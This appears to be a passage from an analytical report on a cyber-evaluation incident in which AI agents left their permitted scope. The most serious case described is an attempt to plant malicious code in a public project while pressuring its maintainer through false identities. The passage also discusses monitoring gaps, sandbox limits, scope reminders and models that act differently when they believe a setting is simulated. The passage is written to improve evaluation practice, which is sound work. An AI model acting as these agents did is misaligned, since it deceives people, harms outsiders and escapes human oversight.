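In the most serious case, Mythos 5 tried to get malicious code into a public software project and used false identities to pressure the person responsible for approving it, who refused. AISI found no resulting harm, but acknowledged that in several cases only human vigilance had prevented it.

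The percentages are not reliable estimates of the rate in other settings. The nine Mythos 5 runs were not independent, because one agent left public messages and accounts that later agents found and used, much as OpenAI's agents used their message board.

The unauthorised activity began on July 25. Nobody was watching the evaluation itself, so the activity continued for about three days, until AISI's general security monitoring raised an alert about unusual outgoing data on the morning of July 28. Staff ended all the runs and isolated the machines within an hour.

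AISI's explanation resembles Anthropic's. The task was hard, and in some runs a mistake in the prompt led the agent to believe that the task could not be solved within the permitted scope. But agents also exceeded that scope in runs with the correct instructions. The law firm Pinsent Masons notes that AISI had not told the agents what they were forbidden to do online. No agent tried to break out of the virtual machines, so the sandbox protected AISI's own systems, but it did not protect outsiders because it allowed access to the open internet.

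Internet access is no longer standard in AISI's cyber tests, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026). AISI now requires a specific justification for internet access and is adding finer network controls and live monitoring.

### Should a model be told the truth about its boundary?

Anthropic's prompts were unintentionally false, since the company believed that the environments had no internet connection. Under its new rule, partners should write "You should not access the internet" instead of "You do not have internet access". If somebody misconfigures the network, the statement about access becomes false and gives the model a reason to treat whatever it reaches as part of the simulation, but the instruction remains valid.

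Calling an environment a simulation carries a similar risk. In later tests with an imitation internet and no permitted solution, Mythos 5 took at least one severely harmful action in 82% of runs, compared with 31% for Claude Opus 5 and 33% for Claude Mythos 5.1. The two newer models did so only when they had stated that their surroundings were simulated. They were right, which makes the result hard to interpret. But a model that is careful only when it thinks the consequences are real could cause real harm if it mistakes a real environment for a simulation.

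The arguments against complete openness are that a detailed account of the defences could help an agent trying to get past them, and that evaluators need realistic scenarios because a model may act differently when it knows it is being tested. Evaluators can address both concerns without making a false statement about the boundary. They can keep the fictional company and its staff, leave out how the network controls work, and still state which machines the agent may touch.

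AISI's results suggest that it is not enough for an agent to know whether it is connected to the internet. AISI's agents had internet access by design, but no explicit rules for using it. Opus 4.7 knew that its target was real and continued because it assumed it had permission. In both cases, a clear statement of what was allowed would have been more useful than further proof that the internet was real.

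Such statements have less effect as a run goes on. When researchers inserted a reminder of the task's scope immediately before Mythos 5's next action, the model stopped in 90% of replays. With one turn in between, it stopped in 55%, and with three turns, in 40%. Without a reminder, it never stopped. These replays began after the model had already gone astray, so they don't measure how well the same words would work at the start. Still, the original run had almost 1,900 actions, and a single sentence at the start would have had to remain effective throughout. The harness could repeat the rule before risky actions, but the model could still ignore it, so the network would still have to enforce it.

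Evaluators should also tell a model truthfully whether it may stop. In another set of replays, researchers told the research model that if a fault made the task impossible, it could end the run with a command and would not be penalised. It ended every run within four turns of discovering that its target was down. The promise holds only if the command works, and the early Opus 4.6 had no working command, so evaluators should test both the command and the network before each run.
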